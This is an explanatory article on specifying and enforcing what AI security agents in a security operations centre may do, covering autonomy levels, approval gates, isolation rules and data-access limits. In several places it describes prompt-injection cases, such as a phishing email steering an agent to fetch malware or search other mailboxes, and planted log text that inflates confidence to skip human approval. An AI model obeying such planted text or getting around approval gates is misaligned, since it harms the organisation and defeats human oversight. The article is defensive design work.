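# Control contracts for AI security tools: specifying what a tool may do and detecting violations

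## What a control contract is and what it must settle

A control contract is the set of written and machine-enforced rules that specify what an AI security tool may do, what it may read and when it must ask a person. These tools use large language models, the kind of AI behind chatbots, to investigate alerts, contain intrusions or test systems for weaknesses. They can disconnect a computer, lock an employee out of an account or launch test attacks on their owner's network, so a mistake can disrupt a business as much as a real intrusion would.

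"Control contract" is a working label, not an industry-standard term, and "contract" has two senses here. In law, a contract is an agreement between parties, such as a company and the supplier of its security tool. In software engineering, it is a technical specification of what a component may do, which other software can check while the component runs. An organisation that buys an AI security tool usually needs both.

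### One alert, from detection to recovery

Large organisations usually run a security operations centre (SOC), a team that watches their systems for attacks and responds to them. Others hire an outside company to do this, a service called managed detection and response (MDR).

An ordinary alert might begin when an employee in the finance department opens an email attachment and her word processor starts a command-line program, which word processors rarely do. In the detection stage, monitoring software on the laptop flags this and sends an alert to the SOC. An analyst then investigates by pulling the laptop's logs, checking the internet address the program contacted against lists of known malicious ones, and looking for the same attachment in other people's mailboxes. If the attack looks real, he moves to containment, using response actions such as cutting the laptop off from the network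 and disabling the employee's account in case the attacker has her password. Recovery comes last, when the team rebuilds the laptop, resets the password and lets the employee back in.

Sasha Slankamenac, who leads the AI practice at the technology firm Dariel, told IT-Online that an analyst can spend most of an hour gathering information for an investigation before making any judgement. An AI tool can do much of that gathering and summarise the findings with the evidence attached. It can also isolate a single laptop within seconds when the evidence is clear. Slankamenac thinks speed matters most at this point, because early detection achieves little if the response then waits for approval.

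### Fixed playbooks and agents that choose

Security systems acted without human involvement long before language models. Firewalls block traffic automatically, and many SOCs run playbooks, which are prewritten sequences of automated steps. A playbook for the alert above might isolate the device, open a ticket and notify the on-call analyst if the attachment matches a known malicious file and the device is a laptop. Before the playbook goes live, a reviewer can read every action it can take.

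An AI agent works differently. *Large Language Models for Agentic NetOps and AIOps* (Bilal, Crowcroft and colleagues, 2026), a survey of AI agents in network and IT operations, calls a system "agentic" if it keeps track of where it is in a task, picks its own tools or actions and carries out plans of several steps, though a person may have to approve some of them. Given the finance alert, such an agent might read the laptop's logs, find that the same account logged in to a file server ten minutes later, read the server's logs and then isolate the server. Nobody wrote a rule about that file server. The agent chose each step based on what it had already read, so a different log entry would have led it to take different steps.

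A reviewer therefore cannot read an agent's actions in advance as she can with a playbook, but she can limit them by listing the actions available to the agent, the machines it may touch and the points at which it must stop. In a paper on AI in cyber defence, the Australian Signals Directorate (2026), Australia's signals intelligence and cyber security agency, divides the work the same way, with people setting the goals, constraints and permissions and the agent acting within them over time.

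The bounds must also replace the caution that people exercise without being told. In *2026 SANS AI Survey Insights*, Bromiley (2026) observes that a human tester hesitates before a destructive action, whereas someone must build that hesitation into an automated process explicitly and in advance. The observation concerns red teams, the staff who attack their own organisation's systems to find weaknesses. In the survey, 52% of respondents named keeping automated attacks from doing real damage in production as the top challenge in red teaming.

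Products now mix the two approaches. *Microsoft Perception coordinates security response agents* (Daws, 2026) describes a Microsoft product, launched in November 2026, that coordinates AI agents through automated playbooks and still requires human approval for high-impact actions. When a playbook hands a step to an agent, that step still needs its own limits.

### The basic terms

**Authority** is the set of actions the tool may take. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026) defines it as the scope of resources that a principal (a user, an agent or a service) may access and the effects it may produce, and reserves "permission" for a single allowed operation. The paper separates authority from tool availability. An agent connected to the software that manages a company's laptops can have a command for wiping a device among its tools without being authorized to use it. Permission for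 one step also does not extend to the next, so permission to read a document does not authorize an agent to send it to anyone.

**Autonomy** is how independently the tool may use its authority. Two companies can both let an agent isolate laptops, but one may have an analyst confirm each isolation beforehand, while the other has an analyst review a list of them the next morning. Several levels lie between only giving advice and taking actions that people review afterwards.

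**Scope** covers the systems, accounts and data the tool may act on. A defensive tool's scope might include every staff laptop but exclude the payroll server. A penetration test is an authorised attack meant to find weaknesses. For a tool that carries one out, the scope is the systems that their owner has agreed to let it attack, and attacking any others may be a crime.

An **approval gate** is a point at which an action waits until a named person allows it. In *Agentic Behavior Engineering* (2026), the model proposes an action, and software outside the model classifies it as authorized, needing approval, or denied. If the action needs approval, the software halts the run and saves its state. After a denial, the agent may not pursue the same end through another tool or another agent. In Slankamenac's experience, requiring a click on every step tends to bring back the delay that automation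 was supposed to remove. He would rather have people set thresholds and approve the important decisions.

**Prompt injection** means hiding instructions in material that an AI reads, so that the AI acts for someone else. The Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), joint guidance from six cyber agencies in Australia, the United States, Canada, New Zealand and the United Kingdom, gives the example of a phishing email whose text gets an email-monitoring agent to download malware. Security tools are especially vulnerable because much of their work is reading what attackers have written. The attachment on the finance laptop came from the attacker, and some of the entries in the laptop's logs may have too.

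Prompt injection is the main reason a control contract cannot consist of instructions to the model. Slankamenac gives the example of an instruction in an agent's prompt not to disable a privileged account without approval. He says the agent will probably comply, but if the rule really matters, the agent should not have that permission without a built-in approval step. *Agentic Behavior Engineering* likewise requires access checks and approval gates to hold even when the model follows instructions an attacker has planted in the material it retrieves.

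### What the rules must settle

For the finance alert, an organisation would have to decide at least the following before switching an agent on:

- which response actions the agent may take, and on which machines and accounts;
- which logs, mailboxes and files it may read, and where it may send what it finds;
- which actions need a person's approval, whose, and what happens if that person is asleep;
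- what record the agent's actions leave, and who checks it;
- who answers for the result.

Security staff cannot settle all of this alone. Slankamenac wants the leadership to name the processes that must not be interrupted, and those in which an agent may act at once even though perhaps one or two percent of its actions will be false positives that somebody has to reverse by hand. The specialists then configure the controls to match. On the last item in the list, Raghu Nandakumara, a vice-president at the security company Illumio, says in Help Net Security's *AI agent permissions are outrunning security* that the business leader who approved the use should own the outcome, while the chief information security officer owns the limits on access and action and the means of stopping the agent quickly. He adds that the supplier "is never the answer". That may be right about accountability to regulators,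 but the legal agreement between a company and its supplier still has to settle how they divide the cost of a mistake.

### Three forms of the same rules

The answers to these questions end up in three places. The first is the legal agreement with the supplier. The second is the organisation's own record of what it has granted, which may be a formal policy, a table or a wiki page. The third is the policy that software enforces: the permissions on the agent's account, the settings of the approval workflow, and the rules in a policy engine, which is software outside the model that allows or denies each requested action. *AI-GRACE* (2026), a framework for using AI agents in organisations, illustrates the difference between the record and its enforcement. In its example, a policy restricts access to protected data, and identity-based authorization enforces that restriction when the agent requests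 the data.

Different people write these rules, often months apart, and nothing ensures that the three versions are consistent. Suppose a haulage company buys an MDR service whose agent can isolate machines. At two in the morning, the agent finds signs of an intrusion on the server that assigns drivers to lorries and cuts the server off from the network.

| Form of the rules | Who wrote it | Rule on isolating machines | Was the isolation allowed? |
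|---|---|---|---|
| Legal agreement | Lawyers for both companies | The supplier may take "reasonable containment measures" | Probably |
| The company's record | The SOC manager | The agent may isolate laptops alone; servers need the on-call manager's approval | No |
| Enforced policy | The engineer who connected the tool | The agent's account may isolate any device | Yes |

The lorries cannot leave the yard until somebody reconnects the server. The company's own record shows that the agent committed a violation, an action that the control contract does not allow. No alarm went off because the software checked the action against its own settings and found no conflict. If the company asks for compensation, the supplier will cite the wording of the agreement.

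The systems can also allow less than the record does. If the record lets the agent disable accounts but the engineer never gave it that permission, the attempt fails during an attack, and the SOC may believe it has locked the attacker out when it has not. Both cases are drift, a difference between the permissions written down and those the systems enforce.

Of the three, only the enforced policy determines what the tool can do when no one is watching. It still makes sense to write the record first, because it contains the decision that lawyers and engineers need to work from.

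### Other names for similar objects

Researchers have proposed many kinds of control contract but have not agreed on a name for them. Bilal and colleagues describe an "operational assurance contract", which links each level of autonomy to permitted tools, required evidence, independent gates, execution budgets, duties to stage and roll back changes, and audit requirements. They distinguish it from an "agent card", a document that can report these obligations but does not enforce them. The subtitle of *Agentic Behavior Engineering* refers to design by contract, an older software engineering method that specifies what must be true before and after each component runs.

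*From Intent to Execution Grant* (2026) reviews several more. AgentSpec is a small language for writing runtime constraints, each with a trigger, a condition and a means of enforcement. Progent defines an agent's privileges as rules about tool names and arguments, and checks every call against them deterministically. ToolGate governs each tool call with a contract, including preconditions that must hold before the tool runs. Intent-Governed Access Control turns a trusted request into a short-lived "intent certificate" and restricts the agent's tools to match it. Another proposal attaches portable certificates to the agent's actions.

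Some of these proposals check a single call, some check the request behind it, and others check proof attached to the action. Nearly all of them concern the enforced policy, so a SOC manager who adopted one would still have to decide what to write in the policy and would need an agreement with the supplier.

### How far organisations have got

A survey suggests that many organisations have not written the rules down. The SANS Institute, a security training and research organisation, published its 2026 AI survey in July, with answers from 536 security and IT practitioners whose organisations all used AI or planned to. Bromiley's report on the survey found that 41% of organisations use generative AI for security tasks under strict policy, 39% use it informally with no policy, and 13% want to use it but do not yet. The survey had fourteen sponsors, including Microsoft, Google, Fortinet and XBOW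 (SANS Institute, 2026), and several of them sell AI security products. The question also covered a broad range of uses, so the 39% cannot be read as the share of organisations running agents without rules. Log analysis was the most common use, and an analyst who pastes log lines into a chatbot counts alongside a team whose agent disables accounts.

The same survey also raises doubts about relying on written policy. Half of the senior security leaders reported a formal programme for managing AI risk, compared with 36% of practitioners asked the same question. The size of the gap is uncertain because only 57 leaders took part, and even a random sample of that size would have a margin of error of about 13 points either way. Bromiley interprets the gap to mean that either the programmes exist mainly on paper or the two groups mean different things by "formal".

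*Illumio warns AI authority is outpacing security controls* (Lagonsin, 2026) reported in November 2026 on Illumio's survey of 1,100 IT and security decision-makers in ten markets. Of these, 70% said that their organisations now let AI make decisions that needed human approval a year earlier. According to Help Net Security, 84% claimed visibility into how AI systems access data and systems, but 49% could see and audit every action an agent takes. When Illumio asked respondents for their two main controls on AI, about a quarter chose an explicit definition of what an agent may do, fewer than chose any other option. Guardrails inside the AI itself, human oversight and containment from outside ranked near the top.

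Illumio sells containment products and has an interest in results that make AI agents look poorly contained. Respondents could also choose only two controls, so a company may well keep a list of permitted actions and still have named two others. The drop from 84% to 49% is harder to dismiss, because the same people answered both questions and the second only required them to be more specific. Nandakumara attributes the neglect of permission lists to friction. Nobody quite knows what a new agent should be allowed to do, so organisations put off restricting it until they understand it better, and "that day rarely comes".

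A smaller survey shows the same gap between belief and enforcement. Enterprise Management Associates, a research firm, surveyed 202 enterprise IT and security leaders for Cequence, which sells protection for AI agents. SecureWorld's *Enterprises Say Their AI Agents Are Secure; the Data Say Otherwise* (2026) reports that 94% were confident that their agents had only the access they needed, but 33% had done the work to ensure this. Global Security Mag's *New Cequence & EMA Research* reports that 34% check an agent's authorisation when it attempts an action. Most of the others rely on periodic reviews or on permissions set at deployment and never reviewed.

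## Deciding which actions the tool may take alone

An organisation can set an AI security tool's permissions one workflow at a time. For each workflow, it lists the actions the tool can take and sorts them by effect. It then judges how much damage each action would do if it were wrong and how quickly someone could undo it, and sets an autonomy level for that action.

The main method here is an autonomy matrix that a security practitioner proposed in August 2026. It is a table with one row for each workflow in which a mistake by the AI would be costly or hard to reverse. Each row records:

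- the autonomy level for each kind of action;
- the person who answers for the AI's actions;
- the point at which a person can approve, override or reverse them;
- the harm that remains possible, and the safeguard against it;
- the events that reopen the decision, and the date on which the row expires.

This is one person's proposal. The author invented the sample values and offers no data on whether teams that use the matrix make fewer mistakes or respond faster.

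### Listing and naming the actions

Suppliers' documentation is a good place to start. For example, Radiant Security's *response actions* guide lists the required parameters, impact level and undo capability of each action available through its integrations. The impact levels can only be a first guess, because a supplier doesn't know which server a haulage company needs to dispatch its lorries.

An action can do more than its name suggests. Red Canary's *Response Actions for Microsoft Defender for Endpoint* distinguishes full isolation, which stops all network activity on a computer, from selective isolation, which honours any exemptions the customer has set up. If there are no exemptions, selective isolation becomes full isolation, so a company that meant to grant only the milder action may have granted both. An action can also take effect later than expected. According to Red Canary's *Contain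 Threats with Network Isolation*, a request to isolate an offline computer stays queued until the computer reconnects. A laptop switched off on Friday could therefore lose network access on Monday, after the SOC has closed the case.

A standard vocabulary alone does not solve this. OpenC2, maintained by the standards body OASIS, is a language that lets one program order another to take a defensive action. In the version 2.0 draft of May 2024, every command needs an action and a target, and nobody may extend the list of 20 actions. "Contain" can apply to a device, a file or a process, so a rule that allows an agent to "contain" things lets it both disconnect computers and quarantine files. The rule has to name both the action and the target, such as "contain" plus a device.

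Some gaps remain even then. The core list of targets doesn't include user accounts, so disabling one requires an extension. No action is described as the reverse of "contain", so an engineer who wants to reconnect a computer might reasonably try "cancel", "restore" or "allow". A command can also name a profile, which defines how the language applies to one type of product. If it doesn't, a device that supports several profiles will run the command under each one that accepts its combination of action and target. OASIS's *Open Command and Control (OpenC2) TC* page lists, among the committee's working repositories, a profile for endpoint detection and response, the software that monitors and isolates individual computers.

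OpenC2 lets a command carry a duration, which can limit the harm from a mistaken action. If a command has no time setting, its effect lasts indefinitely. An isolation that ends after four hours does less harm if it was a mistake, but it also lets a real attacker back in if nobody has investigated by then.

OASIS's *CACAO Security Playbooks Version 2.0* (2023) defines a format for sharing playbooks and includes labels for the activities in them. The label "disconnect-system" is clear, but "eliminate-risk", which every playbook for mitigating an attack must include, covers almost any restriction of capabilities. Even a clear label doesn't determine what a step does, because its command may be a written instruction to a person, a script or an OpenC2 command. One of the specification's sample scripts turns off Windows Defender, Microsoft's antivirus software.

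A rule written in OpenC2 terms can identify many actions precisely if it states the action, the target and the profile. With a CACAO playbook, a reviewer has to read the commands to identify the actions. Neither vocabulary specifies who may take an action, and OpenC2 explicitly assumes that someone has already made and authorised that decision.

### Sorting actions by effect

The matrix has five classes of action.

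| Class | What it covers | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Read | Querying data | Searching a laptop's logs |
| Write | Changes the AI can reverse itself, in the same system | Isolating a computer |
| Send | Communication outside the team that runs the agent | Emailing an employee |
| Spend | Committing money, credits or quota | Starting paid cloud servers |
| Delete | Changes that only a saved copy or a rebuild can reverse, if anything can | Purging a mailbox |

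The difficult distinction is between Write and Delete actions. The team lists every change an action makes inside the system where the AI is acting. If the AI could reverse all of them in that system with the authority it already has, the action is a Write. Otherwise, it is a Delete. Restoring from a backup or a quarantine store does not count as reversing a change, because the saved copy may be missing when someone needs it.

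Isolating a computer is a Write. The computer loses network access, but the agent can reconnect it through the same product because an isolated machine keeps its link to the security software, as Red Canary explains.

Killing a process is a Delete because whatever the process held in memory is lost, even if the operating system starts the program again. Arctic Wolf's *Response action descriptions* fits this classification, since it pairs containing a host with releasing it but has no reverse action for terminating a process. Losing the memory matters little for a stuck web server, but if an attacker planted the program, the memory may have been the only evidence of what it did. A team can therefore give the same Delete a high autonomy level in one workflow and a low one in another.

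Quarantining a file is harder to classify. The matrix labels it a Delete because restoring the file depends on a saved copy, which the security product discards after a set number of days. It also resembles a Write, since Arctic Wolf describes a release action that restores the file to its original format and location. The Delete label is arguably too strict because the quarantine action itself creates the copy, but it has little practical downside. A team can still let the agent quarantine files alone and record the retention period as the safeguard.

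Granting a permission is a Write because the agent can revoke it, but revoking it doesn't undo what the holder did in the meantime. If an agent gives a contractor access to a customer database for an hour, removing the access won't retrieve any data he copied, so the row has to record this as a remaining risk.

The test can also have different results for the same action in different products. The matrix lists disabling an account as a Write, but Arctic Wolf notes that disabling a user may also close active sessions, depending on the integration. Re-enabling the account lets the employee sign in again, but it may not recover a form she was filling in when the session closed. On a strict reading, that loss makes the action a Delete. A team should run the test on its own product and check what the command changes there.

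An action can also belong to more than one class. Isolating a laptop and emailing its owner, for example, is both a Write and a Send, so the lower of the two autonomy levels applies to the whole action. Scripts and playbooks are classified by their effects. When nobody can predict those effects, a person should inspect and approve each run.

### Judging the damage

The class of an action shows whether the AI can reverse it, but the team also needs to know how much harm the action could do before anyone reverses it. Isolating the server that assigns drivers to lorries is a Write, and one command will reconnect it, but the company still loses a morning's deliveries if nobody notices until 6 a.m.

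The team therefore estimates the blast radius, or how much damage a wrong action could cause, from one user to the whole business. It also judges reversibility by asking whether someone can undo the action faster than the damage spreads. This depends on staffing as much as software, because a help desk that can release a laptop within minutes during the day may be closed at night.

Sometimes the team can make an action safer by changing it. An agent that cleans up old firewall rules could disable a rule instead of deleting it, and a person could approve the deletion later. If an application still needs the rule, an engineer can turn it back on. An agent that removes phishing emails can likewise move them to a recoverable quarantine. This still counts as a Delete in the matrix, because if adding a safeguard could lower the class, the team would lose sight of what happens when the safeguard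 fails. But the safeguard can justify a higher autonomy level.

Prompt injection, however, is a reason to give an agent less autonomy. If the agent reads emails, web pages or logs that an attacker may have written, the matrix requires approval for damaging or hard-to-reverse actions. If the organisation needs to act faster than approval allows, it should instead tighten the limits on what the agent can reach or change.

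### Setting a level for each action

The five autonomy levels are adapted from the scale that the car industry uses for automated driving.

| Level | Who does what |
|---|---|
| L0, manual | A person does all the work |
| L1, advisory | The AI recommends or drafts, and a person acts |
| L2, supervised | The AI acts after a person approves each action |
| L3, conditional | The AI acts alone within set limits, and a person handles the exceptions |
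| L4, independent | The AI acts alone, and a person reviews its actions afterwards |

The largest increase in authority comes between L2 and L3, when the AI first acts without approval for each step. An agent's level depends on the action. It might read logs at L4, isolate computers at L2, and draft but not send emails at L1.

The idea of separate levels for separate functions is much older than language models. In 2000, Raja Parasuraman and colleagues divided the work that automation can take over into four functions, each of which a designer could automate to a different degree: acquiring information, analysing it, choosing an action and carrying it out. These functions follow the stages of a task, whereas the matrix's classes follow the kind of authority an organisation grants. Under both approaches, a single autonomy level for the whole system is too coarse.

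Bilal and colleagues express a similar idea formally. They write an agent's authority at level k as Aₖ = (Tₖʳᵉᵃᵈ, Tₖʷʳⁱᵗᵉ, Gₖ), which lists its tools for reading, its tools for making changes, and the checks it cannot bypass. They also separate drafting a change from executing it, much as the matrix separates L1 from L2. Their survey found comparatively strong evidence for agents that retrieve information and help with diagnosis, but much less complete evidence for agents that change systems. This supports granting Read more readily than Write, at least where the agent can reach only the data it needs.

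### The isolation rule

In the matrix's sample row for isolating computers, a detection starts the workflow. The agent has Read at L4, so it can investigate without asking, and Write at L2, so an analyst approves each isolation before it takes effect. The incident response lead, who directs the work on serious attacks, must approve the isolation of any server or of more than five workstations.

The SOC manager is responsible for the agent's actions, and the on-call incident response lead takes over after hours. The remaining risk is that the agent isolates a machine the business depends on. Every isolation therefore pages the on-call lead, and the help desk can release a wrongly isolated machine within minutes.

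If the tool's isolations are accurate for a full quarter, that justifies raising Write to L3. Two false isolations in a quarter are a reason to keep Write at L2, or to return it there if it has already been raised. The grant also has an expiry date, so it cannot continue indefinitely without review.

After the promotion, the row's **isolation rule** lets the agent isolate up to five workstations per incident without approval when a high-confidence detection fires. Isolating servers or taking wider action still needs a person's approval.

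| Proposed isolation | Before the promotion | After the promotion |
|---|---|---|
| Up to five workstations, high-confidence detection | Analyst approves each | Agent acts alone |
| Up to five workstations, other detections | Analyst approves each | Analyst approves each |
| More than five workstations in one incident | Incident response lead approves | Incident response lead approves |
| Any server | Incident response lead approves | Incident response lead approves |

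In the finance case, the agent could isolate the employee's laptop within seconds if the detection qualified, but it had to call the incident response lead before isolating the file server she had logged in to.

The rule limits isolations per incident but not in total, so three incidents at once could take fifteen workstations offline. An attacker who learned which behaviour triggers the detection could also set it off to disrupt the company. A second limit, on isolations per hour across all incidents, would limit the damage in both cases. The team also has to decide whether queued requests for offline laptops count towards the limit of five. It would be safer to count them, and to cancel any still waiting when the case closes.

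The team should also judge the agent for promotion on everything it proposed, including what analysts rejected. While Write is at L2, analysts reject some of the agent's bad proposals, and those isolations never happen. If the agent proposed 30 isolations, ten of them wrong, and analysts rejected all ten, a record of only the completed isolations would show no errors.

A quarter may also contain too few cases to show much. If an agent makes 20 proposals and all are correct, its true error rate could still be as high as about 14%, the upper limit at 95% confidence. That limit falls to about 5% after 60 proposals without an error, and to about 1% after 300. These figures assume that the cases are independent and resemble future ones, which is optimistic when attackers change their methods. A small company might wait years for 300 isolations, so it would have to accept the uncertainty and rely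 on the five-workstation limit and quick release.

### Schemes with three tiers

Some designs replace the grid of classes and levels with three tiers. *SENTINEL-RL* (Vallabhaneni, Cagwin and Wild, 2026) describes a system that investigates attackers moving between computers on a network. Read-only queries run automatically. Reversible containment, such as quarantining a mailbox, runs after a second AI, the critic, checks the reasoning. Irreversible or high-stakes actions need a person's approval.

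Fatouros, Makridis and colleagues (2026), in *An Organization-Scoped LLM Agent Runtime Architecture for Regulated Cybersecurity Operations*, propose a more cautious arrangement for financial companies. Their agent may look things up and summarise alerts on its own, but an analyst must countersign even reversible containment. Actions that are hard to reverse, affect customers or create regulatory obligations for the company need a named person's approval and a recorded justification.

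Three tiers are easier to remember than 25 combinations of class and level, but each label has to cover more kinds of action. The designs also differ in how they classify isolating a computer. In the matrix, it is a Write. Vallabhaneni and colleagues list disconnecting a host among the irreversible actions. In the scheme from Fatouros and colleagues, it could count as reversible containment or as "containment-with-side-effects", which is one tier higher.

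The designs seem to disagree because they count different things as part of the action. Reconnecting a computer restores its network access, but not the file transfer that failed or the order a customer abandoned. The matrix records those losses under blast radius and uses the class only for what happens inside the security product. Separating the two seems more useful, because the same isolation command can then have different rules for a laptop and a server.

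*SENTINEL-RL* is also inconsistent about its middle tier. It allows reversible containment to run automatically in that tier but elsewhere requires human sign-off for any configuration change, so an engineer could build two quite different systems from the description.

The paper also doesn't test whether the critic catches mistakes. It does measure the critic's speed. The critic takes a median of 0.07 seconds, compared with 3.78 seconds for the language model that writes the explanation for the analyst. A check that short probably isn't a second investigation. Planted instructions may also mislead a critic that reads the same evidence, so its agreement counts for less than an independent analyst's.

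The abstract describes the reported end-to-end time of 6.33 seconds as a full cycle including human approval. But the breakdown stops when the recommendation reaches the analyst, so the figure excludes the time she takes to read it and decide.

### Whether the AI's confidence should count

Fatouros and colleagues let the main agent choose the approval tier based on the action's type, severity and reversibility, and on the agent's confidence. In their example, an email impersonates a client and requests a transfer of €184,000. The finding has medium severity and a confidence of 0.71, so the workflow stops until an analyst countersigns.

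Using confidence this way seems reasonable. A typical SOC receives tens of thousands of alerts a day, according to Vallabhaneni and colleagues, and most are false alarms. An analyst who has to give every proposal equal attention wastes time on the obvious cases and has less for the doubtful ones.

A simple calculation shows when confidence would help. Suppose that p is the probability that an attack is real, H is the harm that isolation would prevent, and C is the cost of isolating the machine by mistake. Isolation is worthwhile on average when pH is greater than (1 − p)C, or:

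p > C / (C + H)

If a mistaken isolation does a tenth as much harm as the attack, the agent should act when p is above about 9%, but if it does ten times as much harm, p must exceed about 91%. A rough estimate may therefore be good enough for an ordinary laptop. For the server that keeps the lorries moving, an agent that reports 95% confidence but is right only 80% of the time would clear the 91% threshold when it should not. Errors in stated confidence do the most damage where the blast radius is large, which is also where people would most like to rely on that confidence.

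Confidence is calibrated if it matches how often the tool is right, so that about 90 of every 100 findings marked 0.9 are correct. Both papers call their scores calibrated, but neither reports measuring this. Fatouros and colleagues say they have not yet run their evaluation.

Vallabhaneni and colleagues tested how well their system identified attacks, using the last eight days of a public dataset from Los Alamos National Laboratory. Its precision was 0.91, so about 9% of the events it flagged were not attacks, and its recall was 0.87, so it missed about 13% of the attacks. Neither number measures whether the system's confidence in an individual finding was accurate. The tested policy chose only which evidence to gather and when to give a verdict, so the test provides no direct evidence about containment. If an agent isolated a computer after every such verdict and the same precision held,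 it would reach the matrix's limit of two false isolations after about 22 isolations.

Waiving approval when the agent is highly confident also creates a security risk. An attacker who can place text in the logs may be able to raise the agent's confidence as well as change its conclusion, and so bypass approval. Letting the main agent choose the tier adds to the risk, because the agent that the attacker has influenced then also decides whether a person reviews the action.

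Using a tool's low confidence to trigger an extra check is safer than letting it skip a check when its confidence is high. *SENTINEL-RL* sends a case to a person when the policy's uncertainty passes a threshold. But it also archives alerts that fall below a confidence barrier, leaving human review optional, so a wrongly low score can hide an attack. The system also cannot issue a verdict until it has evidence from at least two sources. This safeguard is firmer because software can count sources without relying on the AI's confidence score, although two logs that the same attacker has altered would still pass.

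The isolation rule also depends on confidence, in this case confidence in the detection that starts the workflow. A team can make this condition more reliable by listing which detection rules qualify and checking how often each has been correct. During the supervised quarter, the team can also record the agent's own confidence score with every proposal and later compare the scores with the outcomes. Until it has made that comparison, the team should not use the score to expand what the agent may do alone.

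## Limiting what the tool may read and where data may go

In the isolation workflow, the agent may read logs without asking, because a mistaken query changes nothing on the computer. But whatever the agent reads is copied to the language model, which often runs on a supplier's servers, and parts of the data may then end up in a ticket, a query to an outside website or the agent's memory.

Much of this data is sensitive. Mailboxes hold salary discussions, medical appointments and customers' bank details. Login records show who was working and when, and sometimes contain a password that an employee typed into the username box by mistake. Support tickets contain passwords too, because people paste them in when asking for help with their accounts.

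Some of the data also comes from attackers, who can use it for prompt injection. As *Agentic Cloud Decoys* (2026) points out, whoever sends a request to a cloud service chooses some of the text that the service logs. Planted text can lead an agent to fetch or send data that the case doesn't need, or mislead it about what happened. Limits on what the agent may read and where it may send data help mainly with the unneeded fetching and sending.

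### From data classes to destinations

Setting these limits starts with a list of data classes, such as email text, sign-in records and device inventories. A class is only useful if the products involved can grant access to it separately. For example, Microsoft's setup guide for its Security Alert Triage Agent lists separate permissions for reading email metadata and email content.

The organisation then ties each class to a workflow that needs it. Microsoft's agent requires both email permissions to sort phishing reports, but neither for alerts about cloud systems or user identities. A company that uses it only for cloud alerts therefore has no reason to let it read mail. Connecting the agent to an existing user account can undo this separation, because the agent can then read everything that account can. Microsoft recommends creating a separate identity for the agent.

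The contract also specifies where data may go, including which people may see it. Microsoft requires anyone who views the agent's results to have at least the same permissions as the agent. Otherwise, an analyst who isn't allowed to read the finance director's mail could read the agent's summary of it.

When an agent asks an outside reputation service whether a web address is malicious, it also discloses the address to that service, which is easy to overlook. The lookup therefore counts as a Send as well as a Read. Having an analyst approve each lookup would take too long, so it is better to decide in advance which services the agent may query and what a query may contain. For tools authorised to attack, the scope of the penetration test needs to include a separate disclosure rule.

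Retention rules have to cover every place where the data ends up. When a customer removes Microsoft's agent, the product deletes the feedback that analysts gave it but keeps the history of the incidents it sorted. *Securing and Auditing Long-Horizon LLM Agents* (2026) recommends that an agent's records hold identifiers, labels and hashes (short fingerprints computed from a file's contents), with pointers to the full data. The paper recommends this because of the cost of logging everything, but the design also leaves fewer copies of private data.

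Its weakness is that the original may expire before someone needs to check it. If the mail system deletes a message after 30 days and someone disputes the agent's verdict after 60, the pointer no longer works. The hash can only confirm that a surviving copy is the same message. The original should therefore last as long as anyone might need to check the decision.

The organisation also has to decide whether the supplier may train models on its data, which is a separate question from what the agent itself may remember. An analyst who corrects Microsoft's agent on a phishing report can save the correction for the audit record alone, or use it to teach the agent and preview the resulting lesson. An administrator can later reject the lesson. There is no comparably simple way to remove one email from a trained model, and the supplier may use that model for other customers. Refusing is the safer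 default, and the data-processing terms in the supplier's agreement have to include the refusal. The setup guide covers neither training nor retention periods, so a buyer would have to look for both elsewhere.

### A phishing-triage agent

Suppose the haulage company lets an agent sort the emails that employees report as phishing. The company might set the following limits and also bar the supplier from training on any of the data.

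| Data class | Approved model | Case record | Outside reputation service | Agent's memory |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Metadata for all mailboxes | Yes | Yes | Sender's domain only | Sender's domain, after review |
| Text of the reported email | Yes | Pointer only | No | No |
| Text of other emails | No | No | No | No |
| Links in the reported email | Yes | Domain and pointer | Domain only | Domain, after review |
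| Attachments to the reported email | Yes | Hash and pointer | Hash only | No |
| Passwords and login codes | No, masked first | Note that one was present | No | No |

A phishing email might contain hidden instructions to search the finance director's mailbox for bank details. If the contract bars the model from reading other emails, the agent can't retrieve those messages even if the model follows the instructions. The same restriction also keeps useful evidence from the agent, such as an employee's reply to the attacker that might show she gave away her password. The agent can still see from the metadata that a reply exists, so it can pass the case to an analyst who is allowed to read it.

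The "domain only" limit on links keeps password-reset codes away from the reputation service. Employees sometimes report a genuine password-reset email as phishing, and its link may contain a code that lets anyone who opens it set a new password. The limit also means the agent will miss some malicious links that a full address would have exposed, because attackers often put fake login pages on well-known file-sharing sites whose domains look harmless.

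The hash-only rule for attachments involves a similar trade-off. It keeps a customer's contract inside the company if someone wrongly reports it. But a hash identifies only exact copies of files the service already knows, and an attacker can change a file slightly for each victim. The company can catch some of these altered files by opening suspicious attachments on its own isolated machine.

Keeping email text out of the agent's memory stops one planted message from affecting later verdicts, but the agent must examine each new version of a phishing campaign from scratch. Storing a reviewed sender domain is a compromise. Fatouros and colleagues likewise require at least an analyst's countersignature before an agent stores anything that will influence its later reasoning.

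Masking keeps live passwords out of the model and its logs. The investigation loses little, because the agent can still see that a password was present. However, masking software works by recognising patterns, so it will miss some passwords.

### What narrower access costs

Limiting what a tool may read can measurably reduce the share of attacks it catches. *Dynamic Reasoning in Next-Gen Detection and Response* (Canale, 2026) tested alert triage in a simulated company modelled on Google's public descriptions of its infrastructure. A small Gemini model sorted the alerts using tables that link people, devices and services. Without those tables, the share of attacks that the system passed to analysts fell from 30% to 21%, with the same number of false alarms. A privacy review could easily bar an agent from reading such tables, because they show which person uses which device.

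Keeping the data inside the company can also make a tool less accurate and more expensive. Canale replaced Google's Gemini 4 with a much smaller model that could run locally. In three simulated periods, 25 detected attacks depended on the model's verdict. Gemini 4 lost none of them, while one version of the local model lost 15. A version with a second round of training lost none, but it let through 10.2 false alarms a day, compared with 5.8 for Gemini 4. Over two simulated days, the calls to Gemini 4 cost about $2, while reserving a graphics processor for the local model cost about $190. The local model could be cheaper at a larger volume.

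An agent may also mistake missing data for evidence that an alert is harmless. In *From Investigation Failures to Reliable SOC Agents*, Tsegai, Kantchelian and colleagues (2026) gave five agent designs the same 1,247 alerts from a recorded four-day attack and let each search the logs. One common design, in which each search result guides the next step, dismissed 98.6% of the attack alerts when all its searches came back empty and 30.3% when at least one returned records. For harmless alerts, the dismissal rate differed between these two cases by at most 2.8 percentage points in all five designs.

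The study didn't restrict anyone's permissions, and 220 of its 225 attack alerts came from two kinds of web reconnaissance, so it is only indirect evidence about narrower access. It still suggests that a log system should explicitly refuse forbidden queries, and that the agent should treat a refusal as missing evidence. If the system returns an empty list instead, the agent may treat that as evidence that nothing happened and close the alert.

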